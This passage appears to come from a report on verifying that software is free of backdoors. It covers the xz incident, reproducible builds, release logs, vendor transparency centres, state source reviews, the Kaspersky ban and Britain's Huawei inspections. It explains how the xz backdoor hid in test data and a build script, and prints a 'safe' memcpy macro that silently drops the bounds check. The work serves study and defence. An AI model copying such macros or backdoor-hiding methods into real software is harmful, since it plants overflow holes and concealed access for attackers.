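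The attack used code hidden in the test folder and a script that unpacked it. A compression program has to be tested on damaged and unusual compressed files, so unreadable data in that folder looked normal, as it had in the OpenSSH backdoor of 2002. The script was not in the public repository, only in the release package, which is the archive of source files that distributions download and build. It added the backdoor to the compression library only during the build of a Debian or Red Hat style package for 64-bit PCs.

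On several distributions, the OpenSSH login server loads this library indirectly. The backdoor intercepted one step in checking a visitor's cryptographic key. If the visitor sent a command signed with the attacker's private key, the server ran it. The server behaved normally for everyone else, so guessing could not have triggered the backdoor.

Freund, a Microsoft engineer, was measuring a database's speed on a test version of Debian when he noticed that failed remote logins were using too much processor time and that a login took about 0.8 seconds instead of 0.3. He traced the delay to the compression library and then to the release package. Some test versions of Debian and Fedora already included the backdoor, but it had not reached the stable releases that most servers use. None of the distributions' checks had caught it, and a faster backdoor might have gone unnoticed.

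Reproducible builds would not have exposed the xz backdoor. The release package contained the malicious script, so anyone who rebuilt the library from that package would have produced the same infected library. The package also had a valid signature, because Jia Tan, the maintainer who planted the backdoor, was entitled to sign releases.

Comparing the release package with the repository would have revealed the script. Nobody treated such a difference as alarming, because release packages often contain generated files that the repository lacks. Reproducible Builds (2024) gives another example, from a website that compares the source code used by different distributions. The distributions all had the same source for version 5.9 of the command shell zsh, but it did not match the project's own repository. A better check is to regenerate the release package from the repository and ask for an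 explanation of any remaining differences. Distributions can also build directly from the repository, which in this case would have left the hidden code as an unused test file.

In *VCAligner*, another paper that Reproducible Builds summarises, Li, Jiang and colleagues studied how to match releases of 2,984 Python packages to their source in repositories. The repositories' version labels seemed to identify the right source for 85% of the packages. For the rest, auditors would have had to search more than 10.3 million commits. Matching by file content reduced this to under 65,000. The tool also separates files that exist only in the release from files whose content has changed. The XZ script would have been in the first group.

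These checks can't stop a malicious maintainer, who could have put the script in the repository as well. But other people can read the repository and its history, and somebody might have asked why a build script was unpacking a test file.

### Updates and public logs

A match between source and binary covers only one release. In the "pop-up" attack Wheeler describes, the attacker adds Thompson's changes to the compiler's source in one version and removes them in the next. An inspector who reads only the versions before and after finds clean source both times, but the later binary still carries the backdoor if the infected compiler built it. Wheeler therefore recommends diverse double-compiling for every release or, if this is impractical, at unpredictable times.

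Security updates are the hardest to deal with because customers need them quickly, as attackers may already be using the flaws they fix. Reading the changes can take weeks, but a rebuild is automatic and often takes only hours, so an inspector can reasonably require a matching rebuild before installation and finish the reading afterwards. Debian would have trouble meeting even this requirement, since the rebuilders had reproduced only 82.7% of trixie's security updates for PCs. That percentage is based on few packages, so fixing a handful would raise it considerably.

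The program that installs updates can also let in a backdoor. Nesbitt (2026), in *This Week in Package Management*, reports a flaw that Max Justicz discovered in APT, Debian's package installer. APT could sometimes confuse two downloads, so someone who controlled the network connection could replace a package after APT had verified it and run their own code with full privileges. The customer would have been vulnerable even if an inspector had approved the package and several rebuilders had reproduced it.

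A vendor can also send a special version to a single customer. Inspectors who examine the public release will never see it, and the vendor's signature on it is valid. A public log of released binaries makes this harder. The vendor adds each released binary's hash to the log, which allows additions but no changes or deletions. The customer's device installs an update only if it comes with proof that its hash is in the log. To get the special version installed, the vendor therefore has to record it publicly, where someone may ask what it is.

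The log combines the hashes in pairs, then combines the results in the same way until a single hash represents the whole list. To prove that a release is in a log of a million entries, the vendor needs to supply only about 20 intermediate hashes. A dishonest log operator could still show one list to the targeted customer and another to everyone else, so independent observers have to compare the versions they receive. Google runs a log of this kind for the system software on its Pixel phones, and Go's tools check downloaded packages against another such log. Levsen's list of future work for Debian includes logs that distribute and compare the rebuilders' results.

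A log is only a partial answer, because it records backdoored releases as well as clean ones. SolarWinds would have logged its infected update like any other. The log also can't show what a device is running at a given moment. An intruder who controls the device can display the approved binary and run a different one. Attestation is meant to solve this problem, including in AI data centres.

The log is more useful if somebody rebuilds each release listed in it. Wheeler suggests that government agencies or other trusted organisations could do this for closed products, and publish the hashes of matching source and binaries without releasing the source. Before installing an update, a customer could then check that an inspector had matched it to source code.

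## What inspectors are allowed to see, and what owners risk by showing it

An inspector needs the source code to rebuild a closed product, but a vendor can't take back a copy once it has handed one over. Large vendors therefore keep the code and let inspectors read it through a web portal or in a transparency centre, a facility where approved visitors can examine source code under the vendor's conditions.

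### Microsoft's programme for governments

Microsoft opened parts of the Windows source code to governments in January 2003, when security-conscious agencies were taking an interest in open-source software. Redmond Channel Partner's *Microsoft Opens Source Code to Some Governments* (2003) reports that many people saw the new Government Security Program as an attempt to slow that trend. NATO and a Russian agency were among the first to join. Microsoft's *Government Security Program* now reports more than 40 member countries and international organisations, represented by over 100 agencies.

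An agency starts with the portal, where its staff can search and read selected source code for Windows, Office and other products. Microsoft typically requires this before a visit to one of its centres, which are in the United States, Ireland, Singapore and Brazil. According to Microsoft's *Transparency Centers*, a visit lasts one day to two weeks. Visitors work on Microsoft's computers on a private network. They get a code search engine, programming tools and a disassembler, and can use their own tools with Microsoft's approval. Microsoft's staff can take them through the build process, and they can compare individual binaries with the ones Microsoft ships.

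A two-week visit is short for a product the size of Windows, which has tens of millions of lines of code. At Blaze and colleagues' rate of 100 lines an hour, five reviewers reading for four hours a day would get through 20,000 lines in ten working days. An agency can partly make up for this by continuing to read code on the portal for months, so it makes sense to save the visit for what the portal doesn't allow, such as running tools and comparing binaries.

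### Kaspersky, Cisco and Huawei

Kaspersky, a Russian antivirus company, promised to open its code to inspection in October 2017, a month after the US government ordered federal agencies to remove its products. Press reports had linked its software to the theft of American hacking tools by Russian spies. Co-founder Eugene Kaspersky said the company wanted to show "how we're completely open and transparent" (statement quoted in Fortune, 2017). It opened its first centre for this in Zurich in November 2018, and Kaspersky now lists 13, from Bogotá to Tokyo.

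Kaspersky lets business customers inspect its source code, as well as regulators and state agencies responsible for cybersecurity. It refuses intelligence and law enforcement agencies that have the mandate or the ability to carry out cyberattacks. The refusal protects its other customers but shuts out many of the people who are best at finding backdoors. Britain's National Cyber Security Centre is part of the intelligence agency GCHQ, so a strict reading of the rule would exclude it.

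Visitors to Kaspersky's Transparency Centers choose between three levels of review. The simplest, the "blue piste", is an overview of how the company develops software and handles data. At the deepest level, visitors read the source code with Kaspersky's experts at hand. They can also examine software updates and threat detection rules, the patterns the antivirus program uses to recognise malicious files. They can rebuild a product from source and compare it with the public version. CXO Insight Middle East's *Kaspersky Opens Three New Transparency Centers* (2022) adds that visitors get read-only access and that Kaspersky may turn down a request on security grounds.

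Until July 2023, Kaspersky showed only the code of its main products. It now offers the code of all its "on-premise" products, which run on the customer's own machines. That term does not cover programs that run only on Kaspersky's servers, although the antivirus software sends suspicious files there for analysis.

Cisco, the American maker of network equipment, described narrower terms in Reuters' *More Tech Giants Are Bowing to Russian Demands for Security Secrets* (2017). It sometimes lets regulators inspect small parts of its code in independent laboratories that it trusts, after checking that the code doesn't expose vulnerabilities. Huawei opened a centre in Brussels in March 2019, where customers can examine its source code and test its products. Britain has a separate, permanent team that works only on Huawei equipment.

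### What the restrictions prevent

If the vendor selects the code, the inspector can't claim to have seen all of it. A regulator who reads Cisco's encryption routine can assess that routine, but a backdoor may be in the web page for changing settings. Trying to build the software from the supplied code would show whether anything is missing, but a read-only portal doesn't allow this.

Working on the vendor's computers is a problem if the vendor is the suspect. Inspectors see only what the vendor's software displays, so the vendor could use Boucher and Anderson's reordering trick. A rebuild on the vendor's machine also proves little, because the vendor could have rigged the machine to ignore the source and return a copy of the public binary. Inspectors need to bring their own computer and compiler. They can leave the computer there afterward to keep the code in the building.

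A vendor that approves inspectors' tools learns in advance what they will run and can test a backdoor against the same tools. Requiring approval also hinders inspectors more now that AI models are among the best ways to search a large program. A vendor has good reason to refuse a model that runs on another company's servers, because inspectors would have to send the code there. They can instead run a downloadable model inside the centre, but the strongest models can't be downloaded.

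The strictest rules concern copying. *Tech firms let Russia probe software widely used by US government* (Reuters, 2018) reports that the German software company SAP says it bans recording devices and even pencils from the inspection room. Inspectors then have to rely on memory, so they can't show a puzzling function to a colleague who knows more about it or compare this year's code with last year's.

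Inspectors without a pencil can't easily record a hash of the source, because the most common kind is 64 characters long. If they could take the hash home, they could check on a later visit that the vendor was showing them the same files. Nobody can reconstruct a program from its hash, so the vendor would risk practically nothing by allowing this.

Inspectors who make short visits also fall behind on updates. Kaspersky can change its detection rules daily, and visitors can examine every earlier version, but only after customers have installed it.

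### Few visitors read the code

In the more than three and a half years to July 2022, Kaspersky organised just over 25 visits to its centres. The pandemic must have kept some people away. According to CXO Insight Middle East, most visitors wanted to know how the company manages data, and source code reviews happened "only occasionally". Kaspersky said this was because many organisations lack the skills for such a review, and it offers a course to teach them.

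Kaspersky's *Five years of Transparency* (2023) gives a higher figure, nearly 60 "requesting parties" by June 2023, including national regulators and businesses. This figure covers organisations that received briefings, so it isn't directly comparable with the number of visits, and it doesn't show how many read any code. Six government bodies had taken the course since 2020. When the company opened centres in Rome and Utrecht, it offered only the overview there, because visitors chose that option most often.

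Most other security companies don't offer a review at all. The Tyrol Chamber of Commerce's *Transparency Review and Accountability in Cyber Security* (2025) covers 14 closed-source security products for businesses. In a white paper about the study, Kaspersky counts three vendors with centres for reading source code, and one of the three admits only governments. Kaspersky has an interest in this comparison because it comes out best. A customer who hears that a vendor's code is open to inspection should ask who has inspected it, which version they read and what they could build from it.

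### Russian reviews before sale

Some governments make inspection a condition of entering their market. In Russia, the requests come from the FSB, a security service that approves sophisticated technology products for sale, and FSTEC, a defence agency responsible for countering cyberespionage. Using FSTEC's records, Reuters counted source code reviews of 13 Western products between 1996 and 2013 and 28 in the three years to mid-2017, which is about 13 times as many per year. The increase followed Russia's annexation of Crimea in 2014, but it also followed the Snowden disclosures of 2013, which gave any government reason to check American security products for backdoors.

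The vendor hires a testing laboratory accredited by the Russian authorities. The laboratory's staff read the code in a "clean room", a secure facility the vendor controls. McAfee used its own premises in the United States, and SAP used a site in Germany. IBM, Cisco and Hewlett Packard Enterprise (HPE) also agreed to reviews. Lawyers and US officials said that if a company refused the FSB's request, approval could be delayed indefinitely or denied. Russia's information technology market was worth about $18 billion a year.

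A Russian review of ArcSight's source code alarmed Washington. ArcSight is an HPE program that collects activity records from a network and alerts analysts to signs of an attack, and much of the US military relied on it. Reuters' *HP Enterprise Let Russia Scrutinize Cyberdefense System Used by Pentagon* (2017) revealed that Echelon, a Moscow laboratory, had reviewed the code for FSTEC in 2016. HPE said that the reviewers found no "backdoor vulnerabilities", that its staff supervised them closely at a research centre outside Russia, and that no code left the building.

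Former ArcSight employees feared that Russia could use what it had learned from the review to stop the program from detecting an attack. HPE had not told the Pentagon agency that runs the military's networks about the review, and its contract did not require it to. The agency had not asked to inspect the source code before buying the product, so Russia's testers may have known the code better than the agency that relied on it.

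Echelon's president, Alexey Markov, said that the laboratory has to report vulnerabilities to the Russian government, but does so only after warning the developer and getting its permission. Markov said that "if a vulnerability is found, everyone is happy" because the developer can fix it. Echelon's directors wrote in 2014 that the company had discovered vulnerabilities in half the software it reviewed. The arrangement protects other customers only if Echelon reports every vulnerability it finds. A reviewer who wanted to keep one for the FSB could leave it out of the report, and a flaw such as a missing length check is simple enough to remember without taking notes.

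### How much the source code helps an attacker

Steve Quane of the security company Trend Micro told Reuters it was "incredibly dangerous" to let people look at source code even for a minute, because top researchers can spot vulnerabilities that quickly. Trend Micro refused to let Russia review its TippingPoint software. Chris Inglis, a former deputy director of the NSA, said he wouldn't have shown the code to anybody. After US Senator Shaheen wrote to the Defense Secretary about ArcSight (Shaheen, 2017), the Pentagon replied that Russian and Chinese reviews "may aid such countries in discovering vulnerabilities".

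Several experienced hackers disagreed. Computerworld's *Is source code inspection a security risk* quotes Charlie Miller, formerly of the NSA, who found source code "barely advantageous" in 15 years of hunting for bugs. Peiter Zatko, a former head of cybersecurity research at the US defence research agency DARPA, agreed that researchers find more bugs by analysing binaries and fuzzing them. Steven Bellovin of Columbia University pointed out that a state can reverse engineer any product it buys. He said that if he ran a company like Symantec, he would worry far more about theft of its intellectual property.

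The sceptics are right that Russia didn't need a clean room to attack American software. To exploit a vulnerability in ArcSight, an attacker would first have had to get past the military's other defences. Reuters found no cyberattack in which a source code review had played a part. This is weak evidence, because a victim usually can't tell whether the intruder found the flaw in the source or the binary.

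But "barely advantageous" seems too strong. Source code includes the programmers' comments and identifier names, as well as rarely used functions that a fuzzer never reaches. If reading source gave little help in finding flaws, inspectors would have little reason to ask for it. An inspection that can find a bugdoor will also find accidental vulnerabilities of the same kind, so a vendor can't have a thorough inspection without taking some of this risk.

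The vendor can reduce the risk by searching the code first and fixing what it finds, as Cisco said it did. This leaves fewer flaws for inspectors to learn about, and AI tools have made the search much cheaper. But a dishonest vendor can use the same preparation to remove a backdoor from the copy it shows inspectors. Inspectors should therefore insist on matching that copy to a binary that customers will install.

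The Electronic Frontier Foundation (EFF), a digital rights group, objected that the Reuters reports made an ordinary precaution look malicious. The EFF reviews the code of software it uses, and warned that engineers who rely on secrecy get a false sense of safety. This is a good argument for publishing code so that defenders everywhere can look for flaws, but a weaker defence of the Russian reviews, in which a state laboratory could read code that most customers could not.

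### Vendors who stopped

Symantec, an American antivirus company, stopped accepting government-mandated reviews in early 2016 after concluding that one of the Russian laboratories wasn't independent enough of the state. It could no longer get approval for some of its business products and told Reuters that it did "minimal business" in Russia as a result.

McAfee stopped letting governments review its source code in 2017, after it separated from the chipmaker Intel. Reuters' *McAfee’s Latest Decision Could Change the Way Foreign Governments Conduct Cyber Warfare* (2017) also reports that Micro Focus, the British company that had bought ArcSight, would restrict reviews by "high-risk" governments and require its chief executive to approve them. Neither McAfee nor Symantec said a review had led to an attack. SAP defended its reviews and said it treated all governments alike.

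A company that stops allowing inspections can't take back what earlier inspectors learned. Russia reviewed the source code of Symantec's Endpoint Protection in 2012, and the Pentagon and the FBI were still using the product in early 2018. Symantec said that it had updated the reviewed version many times and that nobody had reviewed the newest one, but updates help only if they happen to replace any flawed code the inspectors saw.

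### China's checks and the limits in trade agreements

A 2017 opinion piece in The Cipher Brief says that China's cybersecurity law, which took effect that June, requires foreign suppliers to submit hardware and software for inspection so that the authorities can verify that the products are "secure and controllable". American trade lawyers told Reuters that China sometimes demands source code reviews before it allows imports of commercial software. Rob Joyce, the White House cybersecurity coordinator, called such demands protectionist.

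The Cipher Brief's article presents design theft as just as serious a concern as vulnerabilities. Clean-room rules protect better against design theft. A competitor who wants to imitate a product needs a large amount of its code, which is hard to memorize, whereas an attacker may need to remember only one line.

Trade negotiators have tried to limit compulsory reviews. As the EFF noted in early 2018, the first completed agreement with such a limit was the Comprehensive and Progressive Trans-Pacific Partnership (CPTPP), which eleven Pacific countries signed that March. Article 14.17 bars members from demanding access to source code as a condition for importing, selling or using software from another member.

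The article applies only to mass-market software and products that contain it, and excludes software used for critical infrastructure. The agreement's digital trade chapter doesn't apply to government procurement, and companies can still negotiate access to source code in commercial contracts. A member can therefore still require inspections of the equipment in its telephone network or its ministries. It would have more trouble requiring them for every home router on sale, and the EFF's concerns included routers and internet-connected cameras.

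In 2020 the United States, Mexico and Canada replaced NAFTA with an agreement that has a similar ban but no exclusion for critical infrastructure. It lets a regulator or court demand source code for a specific investigation or inspection, with safeguards against disclosure. Both agreements also let members take measures to protect their essential security interests. Russia and China signed neither agreement, so the clauses don't apply to the demands that worried American vendors most. In October 2023 the United States withdrew its support for such a clause in talks at the World Trade Organization, to leave itself more room to regulate technology companies at home.

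### The American ban on Kaspersky

In June 2024 the US Department of Commerce banned Kaspersky's antivirus and cybersecurity software from the American market. The department's *Final Determination* (2024) required the company to stop making new agreements on 20 July and stop updating existing customers' software on 29 September.

The department argued that Russia could make Kaspersky act against its customers. Russian law requires the company to help the FSB on request, which Kaspersky did not dispute. Its antivirus software runs in the kernel, with access to everything on the computer, so employees acting on an order could copy a customer's files or install malicious software. They could also leave chosen customers exposed to new malware by delaying the rule that detects it.

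An inspector reading source code would find no sign of a delayed rule. The victim's computer would run exactly the program the inspector had approved, but the program would fail to recognise the malware because an update had not arrived. The department also pointed out that Kaspersky wouldn't need to send malicious code to anyone. It could instead tell Russian hackers which devices run which software, and pass on the new vulnerabilities it learns of early through its worldwide scanning.

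Kaspersky offered two changes to its American operations and staffing. The department replied that employees abroad, including those in Russia, would still have access to the systems that serve American customers. The company also proposed several technical and operational measures, detailed in a confidential appendix. In a public statement, Kaspersky said it had proposed letting a trusted third party verify the security of its products.

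The department judged that none of the technical measures was "completely effective". In particular, they did not adequately address vulnerabilities that might enter the source code during design, which is mostly done outside the United States. No source code review could meet that standard, since even very thorough reviewers miss many flaws. But a lower standard would probably not have saved the company, because the FSB could issue an order the day after a clean report.

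In its formal response, Kaspersky argued that the department lacked a sufficient factual basis for a ban. The company said that its staff in Russia could see only aggregated statistics or data they couldn't attribute to a particular person, and that it had several safeguards against malicious code in its updates. The department answered that Kaspersky's leaders could change its internal data rules at will, and that the company's standard licence agreement listed device identifiers and location among the data its software collects.

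Kaspersky publicly attributed the ban to the geopolitical climate and "theoretical concerns" and complained that the department had not comprehensively evaluated its products. This is a largely fair description of the published decision, which does not allege that anyone had found a backdoor in Kaspersky's software. But the department was trying to judge what the company might do under a future order, and the company's present source code contains little evidence about that. Kaspersky has since closed its transparency centre in Woburn, Massachusetts.

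## Britain's inspection of Huawei equipment

The United States banned Kaspersky's software without alleging that anyone had found a backdoor in it. Britain instead let telephone companies keep buying Huawei's equipment while a permanent team of inspectors examined the source code. It published a report on the inspections every year from 2015 to 2021.

### A centre that Huawei paid for

BT, which runs large parts of Britain's telephone network, told officials in 2003 that Huawei was interested in supplying equipment for a major upgrade. The two companies signed a contract in 2005. Parliament's Intelligence and Security Committee wrote in *Foreign involvement in the Critical National Infrastructure* (2013) that it was shocked that officials had not informed ministers until 2006. The officials knew the government had powers to intervene but thought using them would do too much damage to trade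 and diplomacy.

At first BT managed the risk itself, with help from GCHQ. When other operators began buying from Huawei, the government asked the company for a more formal arrangement. The Huawei Cyber Security Evaluation Centre (HCSEC) opened in Banbury, Oxfordshire, in November 2010. Huawei owned the centre, paid for it and employed its staff. The director, a former GCHQ deputy director, controlled hiring and the budget.

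The inspectors eventually had far better access than visitors to most vendors' transparency centres. They kept source code on the premises, worked on it all year with their own tools, and tested equipment on copies of the operators' networks. They needed Developed Vetting, the clearance that Britain requires of its intelligence officers. Vetting typically took six months, and new recruits worked under escort until they were cleared. One recruit failed the check in 2018 and had to leave.

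Huawei did not begin to release its platform code, the common software underlying its products, until March 2012. GCHQ acknowledged that the delay had been a "major issue", because the inspectors could not fully assess a product without that code.

The committee had assumed that GCHQ ran the centre. When it learned that Huawei did, it called the arrangement "self-policing" and recommended that GCHQ employ the staff. GCHQ replied that Huawei's own employees had more influence over its engineers in China than outside contractors would, and could see the company's internal list of known defects. The committee accepted that this might improve Huawei's engineering, but saw no extra protection against deliberate vulnerabilities. This objection was sound, because an engineer who plants a backdoor doesn't add it to the list of defects.

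In 2008, before the centre existed, GCHQ told the committee that telecommunications equipment contained over a million lines of code and that it was "just impossible to go through that much code" and be certain of the result. The *Government Response to the Intelligence and Security Committee’s Report of Session 2013-14* (2013) described the centre as only one part of the protection, less effective without the other parts. Operators did not have to use the centre, and in 2013 only three of the five that had Huawei equipment did.

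### Oversight from 2014

Kim Darroch, the prime minister's national security adviser, reviewed the centre at the committee's request and decided that its staff should remain Huawei employees. The National Security Adviser's *Huawei Cyber Security Evaluation Centre* (2013) gives two main reasons. Huawei had signed confidentiality agreements with hundreds of suppliers, which would have complicated access for anyone outside the company. Taxpayers might also have faced claims for damages if GCHQ had placed itself between Huawei and its customers. Darroch recommended instead that GCHQ lead the appointment of senior staff and that a new board supervise the centre.

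The board first met in early 2014. Its chair was the GCHQ official responsible for cyber security, who later also headed the National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC), the part of GCHQ that advises on protecting networks. A Huawei executive was deputy chair, and the other members came from government departments, the operators and HCSEC itself. The members aimed for consensus, but GCHQ could decide if they disagreed. Huawei's representatives joined in approving the critical reports of 2019, 2020 and 2021, so it is hard to dismiss the findings as the work of a hostile government.

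GCHQ checked the inspectors' technical competence each year, and the accounting firm Ernst & Young audited their independence. The auditors looked at budgets, hiring, planning and reporting, but not at the quality of the inspections. They reported no major concerns but found lapses. In 2019 Huawei received three reports on low-impact flaws before the NCSC or the operators did.

Huawei also sometimes missed the deadlines for supplying what the inspectors requested, which were 12 weeks for hardware and 30 days for source code. The board saw no harm to the centre's work from these delays. But even 30 days would give a dishonest vendor plenty of time to remove a backdoor from the copy it sends.

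### What 38 people could inspect

At the end of 2018 the centre had 38 staff, according to the HCSEC Oversight Board's *Annual Report 2019* (2019). That year they completed 39 product evaluations, each covering a single Huawei product, and three "solution" evaluations, which cover an operator's whole installation. The HCSEC Oversight Board's *Annual Report 2020* (2020) and *Annual Report 2021* (2021) give the figures for the next two years:

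| | 2018 | 2019 | 2020 |
|---|---|---|---|
| Staff at end of year | 38 | 39 | 39 |
| Product evaluations | 39 | 42 | 24 |
| Solution evaluations | 3 | 4 | 5 |

The pandemic caused the drop in 2020, because staff could examine the code only inside the secure building. The NCSC wanted the centre to evaluate every relevant product at least once every two years, and it met that target on average.

The centre's staff can't have read all the code in the products they evaluated. At the California reviewers' rate of 100 lines an hour, 38 people reading for four hours a day could get through about 3.3 million lines a year. If each of the 39 products had just a million lines, that would be less than 9% of the total, even if the staff did no other work. The board acknowledged that the analysts depended on tools to scan the equipment as a whole, and the centre spent part of each year improving those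 tools.

The inspectors reported several hundred vulnerabilities and other issues to the operators in 2018, and significantly more in 2019. The NCSC attributed the increase to better inspection and a few badly written components, rather than to a decline in Huawei's work. Many of the flaws were serious but basic, such as default passwords, weak encryption, and buffer overflows in code that anyone on the network could reach. Some flaws that the inspectors had reported in earlier versions remained in later ones.

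The NCSC did not believe that the defects were "a result of Chinese state interference". The same elementary errors appeared in many products over many years, which fits poor engineering better than sabotage. But this judgement covered only the defects the inspectors had found, not any backdoor they had missed. Darroch had reached a similar conclusion in 2013, writing that the known vulnerabilities could be explained as genuine design weaknesses or coding errors, though any well-made bugdoor could be explained the same way.

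### Four products and a disorderly build

Britain had always intended to check that the source code in Banbury matched the code running in its networks. HCSEC first tried to show binary equivalence in 2011 and found it didn't have all the source. A team at Huawei's headquarters had been extracting only the parts needed for the features British operators had bought. In December 2016 Huawei promised to supply the complete code and build environments, and it appears to have supplied the full code since 2017. So the inspectors apparently worked from incomplete source for most of the centre's first six years.

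Huawei and HCSEC then chose four products for a pilot in which the binaries could differ if the inspectors could explain the differences. They produced a repeatable build of the first product, which connects broadband customers to the network. But no operator could install that version, because it depended on versions of other software that the operators didn't have.

The other three products came from Huawei's 4G radio, 4G core and optical transmission ranges. Huawei delivered binaries for them during 2018, but HCSEC had not finished validating them by the end of the year. The attempt had exposed problems in the way Huawei built its software:

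- The virtual machines (simulated computers) on which Huawei ran its builds were not clean at the start. Many contained source code left over from earlier builds.
- Some compilers and other tools were long out of support and could produce different output from the same source. Others changed how they optimised the code according to settings on the machine.
- Components with the same version number differed significantly, and some components went back to an older version when the product moved to a newer one.

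HCSEC could not easily recreate many of these build environments, so it could not tell whether a difference between two binaries came from the source, the tools or something left on the machine. Explaining the differences product by product would have taken a great deal of work that had to be repeated for the next release. HCSEC and the NCSC agreed that Huawei should instead redo the whole build process from scratch. HCSEC had described many of the same faults in a 2016 report, but Huawei had rejected its findings.

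Eight years after the centre opened, the inspectors still could not be confident that they were reading the code that ran in British networks. They had found vulnerabilities worth fixing throughout that time, but anyone at Huawei who wanted to hide a backdoor could have left it out of the source code sent to Banbury.

### Seventy copies of one library

In June 2018 the board met at Huawei's offices in Shanghai, where Huawei described how it kept track of the outside software in its products. The NCSC's engineers then picked a component, the encryption library OpenSSL, and had queries about it run on Huawei's live development database. The results showed that Huawei allowed its programmers to use an unmanageable number of versions, including some with known vulnerabilities. Choosing the component on the spot was a good way to test Huawei's account, because Huawei had no chance to prepare.

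HCSEC also compared two major versions of the software for Huawei's 4G base station, the equipment that connects phones to the network by radio. The earlier one contained 70 full copies of four OpenSSL versions and 304 partial copies. The later one contained six full copies of two OpenSSL versions and 17 partial copies. This was a large improvement, but fragments of ten OpenSSL versions remained throughout the code, along with OpenSSL files that Huawei had modified. The newer software was still open to ten publicly known OpenSSL vulnerabilities, some dating from 2006.

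The inspectors also found definitions that made dangerous code look safe. The C function `memcpy` copies a block of data to another place in memory without checking that there is enough room. Huawei's coding rules prohibited such functions and required safer versions, which are also told how much room there is and refuse to copy more than fits. Yet the source contained macros like this one:

```
#define SAFE_LIBRARY_memcpy(dest, destMax, src, count) memcpy(dest, src, count)
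```

Here `destMax` is the space available and `count` is the amount to copy. The macro replaces every call to the "safe" function with a call to plain `memcpy`, which drops the limit. Another macro called a function that was safe, but gave it the amount to copy as the space available, so the check always passed. A reviewer who saw either macro's name elsewhere in the source would think the programmer had guarded against buffer overflows.

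Macros disappear during compilation, so HCSEC counted the calls in the binary of a circuit board that handles data from untrusted networks. About 11% of direct calls to functions like `memcpy` went to unsafe versions. The figure was 22% for functions that copy text and 9% for functions that format text.

The board concluded that some developers "may be actively working to hide bad coding practice". If so, they were probably trying to satisfy Huawei's own rules with as little work as possible, rather than to deceive the British. This complicates a search for backdoors, because an inspector would normally treat disguised code as a strong sign of bad intent, but in Huawei's software it could also come from a programmer trying to meet a deadline.

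### How disorder protects a deliberate flaw

Poor engineering makes a backdoor much harder to find and to prove, though it is not evidence of one. Suppose a product contains 400 accidental buffer overflows and one that somebody planted, and the inspectors find three-quarters of them. They will probably report the planted one, and Huawei will fix it with the rest, but nobody will be able to tell it from the accidental ones. An intelligence service that loses it can look for a replacement among the hundred or so overflows that the inspectors missed.

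A disorderly project also leaves little evidence of intent. Without good records, an inspector who finds a suspicious line can't easily learn who added it or why. The NCSC wanted Huawei to be able to trace every binary back to the code and the programmers behind it, and had been asking for better records since 2010.

Duplicated code adds to the work of inspection. If a product has one standard copy of OpenSSL, an inspector can compare it with the public version in minutes. With 70 full copies, hundreds of partial ones and many files that Huawei has changed, an inspector has to account for each difference and could easily mistake a harmful change for another local adjustment.

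In 2019 Britain's four mobile operators used five versions of Huawei's 5G base station, and HCSEC had to analyse each one. Huawei said all five came from a single global product line, but the NCSC saw no evidence for this, and the patches between them were extremely large. Inspectors who find nothing in one operator's version therefore can't assume another operator's version is clean.

The inspectors couldn't safely concentrate on the most sensitive code either, because many products ran on an old operating system, bought from another company, in which all programs share the same memory.

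### Limited assurance

The board's early verdicts were favourable. In its second annual report, quoted in the Taipei Times (2016), it found that any threats to national security "have been sufficiently mitigated". At the time, Huawei was still sending incomplete source code, and nobody had matched any of it to a binary. The board had good evidence that the inspectors were competent and independent, but much less evidence that they were inspecting the right code.

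The board's 2018 report was the first in which it could no longer give full assurance (Telecoms Tech News, 2019). In 2019 it again offered only "limited assurance" that Britain could manage the long-term risks. That assurance applied mainly to equipment already in use, whose faults the inspectors knew fairly well. As a last resort, the NCSC could tell Huawei exactly how to repair this equipment. The board expected new products to be harder to manage.

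In September 2018, the National Cyber Security Centre (NCSC) asked Huawei for a plan to repair a single product, the 4G base station. Huawei mostly described its existing procedures, and the NCSC and the operators rejected the plan. Huawei then promised to spend $2 billion over five years on changing how it develops software. The NCSC regarded this as a budget for activities Huawei had not yet specified.

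In September 2020 the board disclosed that inspectors had found a more serious problem in 2019. Equipment for fixed-line networks had critical vulnerabilities in the code that handles data arriving from users. The code was very poor, and the old operating system lacked modern defences. Operators had to take what the board called "extraordinary action" to limit the danger. As far as the NCSC knew, nobody had exploited the flaws in Britain.

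HCSEC normally sends its findings to the NCSC, the affected operators and Huawei at the same time. In 2019 it withheld the full details of a vulnerability from Huawei so that Britain could protect itself first. The board did not name the product, but it was probably this one. The delay was sensible because an attacker could use details of a serious flaw until the operators had dealt with it, and the NCSC believed that the Chinese state could compel Huawei to help it.

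Huawei patched the vulnerabilities on time but added a command that switched off some of the product's other protections. An inspector in a different setting might have called this a backdoor. The NCSC attributed it to poor repair procedures and "a complete lack of security awareness".

By the end of 2019, HCSEC had verified binary equivalence for eight product builds. Each match came from a special project for Britain rather than from Huawei's normal build process, so the NCSC doubted that equivalence would last. In its 2021 report, the board again counted eight builds that met the standard during 2020, but it is unclear whether these were the same ones. Huawei committed to providing binary equivalence from December 2020 for official releases of all the network products it sold to British operators.

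Huawei also repaired every vulnerability that HCSEC reported in 2020. Working with the operators, it reduced the number of circuit boards that still needed replacement or a new operating system to 25% of the original. Yet the oversight board saw no overall improvement in the quality of the software. Huawei could fix particular faults when the inspectors pointed them out, but the inspectors kept finding new ones of the same kind.

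### Caps and exclusions

Britain had always combined inspection with other safeguards. GCHQ advised operators to keep Huawei out of the most sensitive parts of their networks and to design the rest so that an attacker would have trouble reaching the equipment. This helps even if inspectors miss a backdoor, because most backdoors are useless to someone who can't send them the trigger. Operators were also supposed to split the 4G equipment that connects customers roughly equally between two suppliers.

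In January 2020 the NCSC (2020) published this advice as a general policy for "high risk vendors". The NCSC judges a vendor partly by the quality of its engineering and partly by matters outside the code, such as whether its home government can give it secret orders and whether that government carries out cyberattacks on Britain. Huawei met the definition of a high risk vendor on several counts. The NCSC cited a Chinese intelligence law of 2017, under which the state could order the company to act against Britain's interests.

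The policy excludes high-risk vendors from a network's core, which identifies customers and directs their traffic, and from sites important to national security. They may supply at most 35% of the base stations in a 5G network and carry at most 35% of its traffic. A similar limit applies to fast fixed-line broadband. An operator may use only one high-risk vendor in a network, and only if the NCSC has designed a plan to manage the risk. HCSEC was part of the plan for Huawei, and no other high-risk vendor had such a plan.

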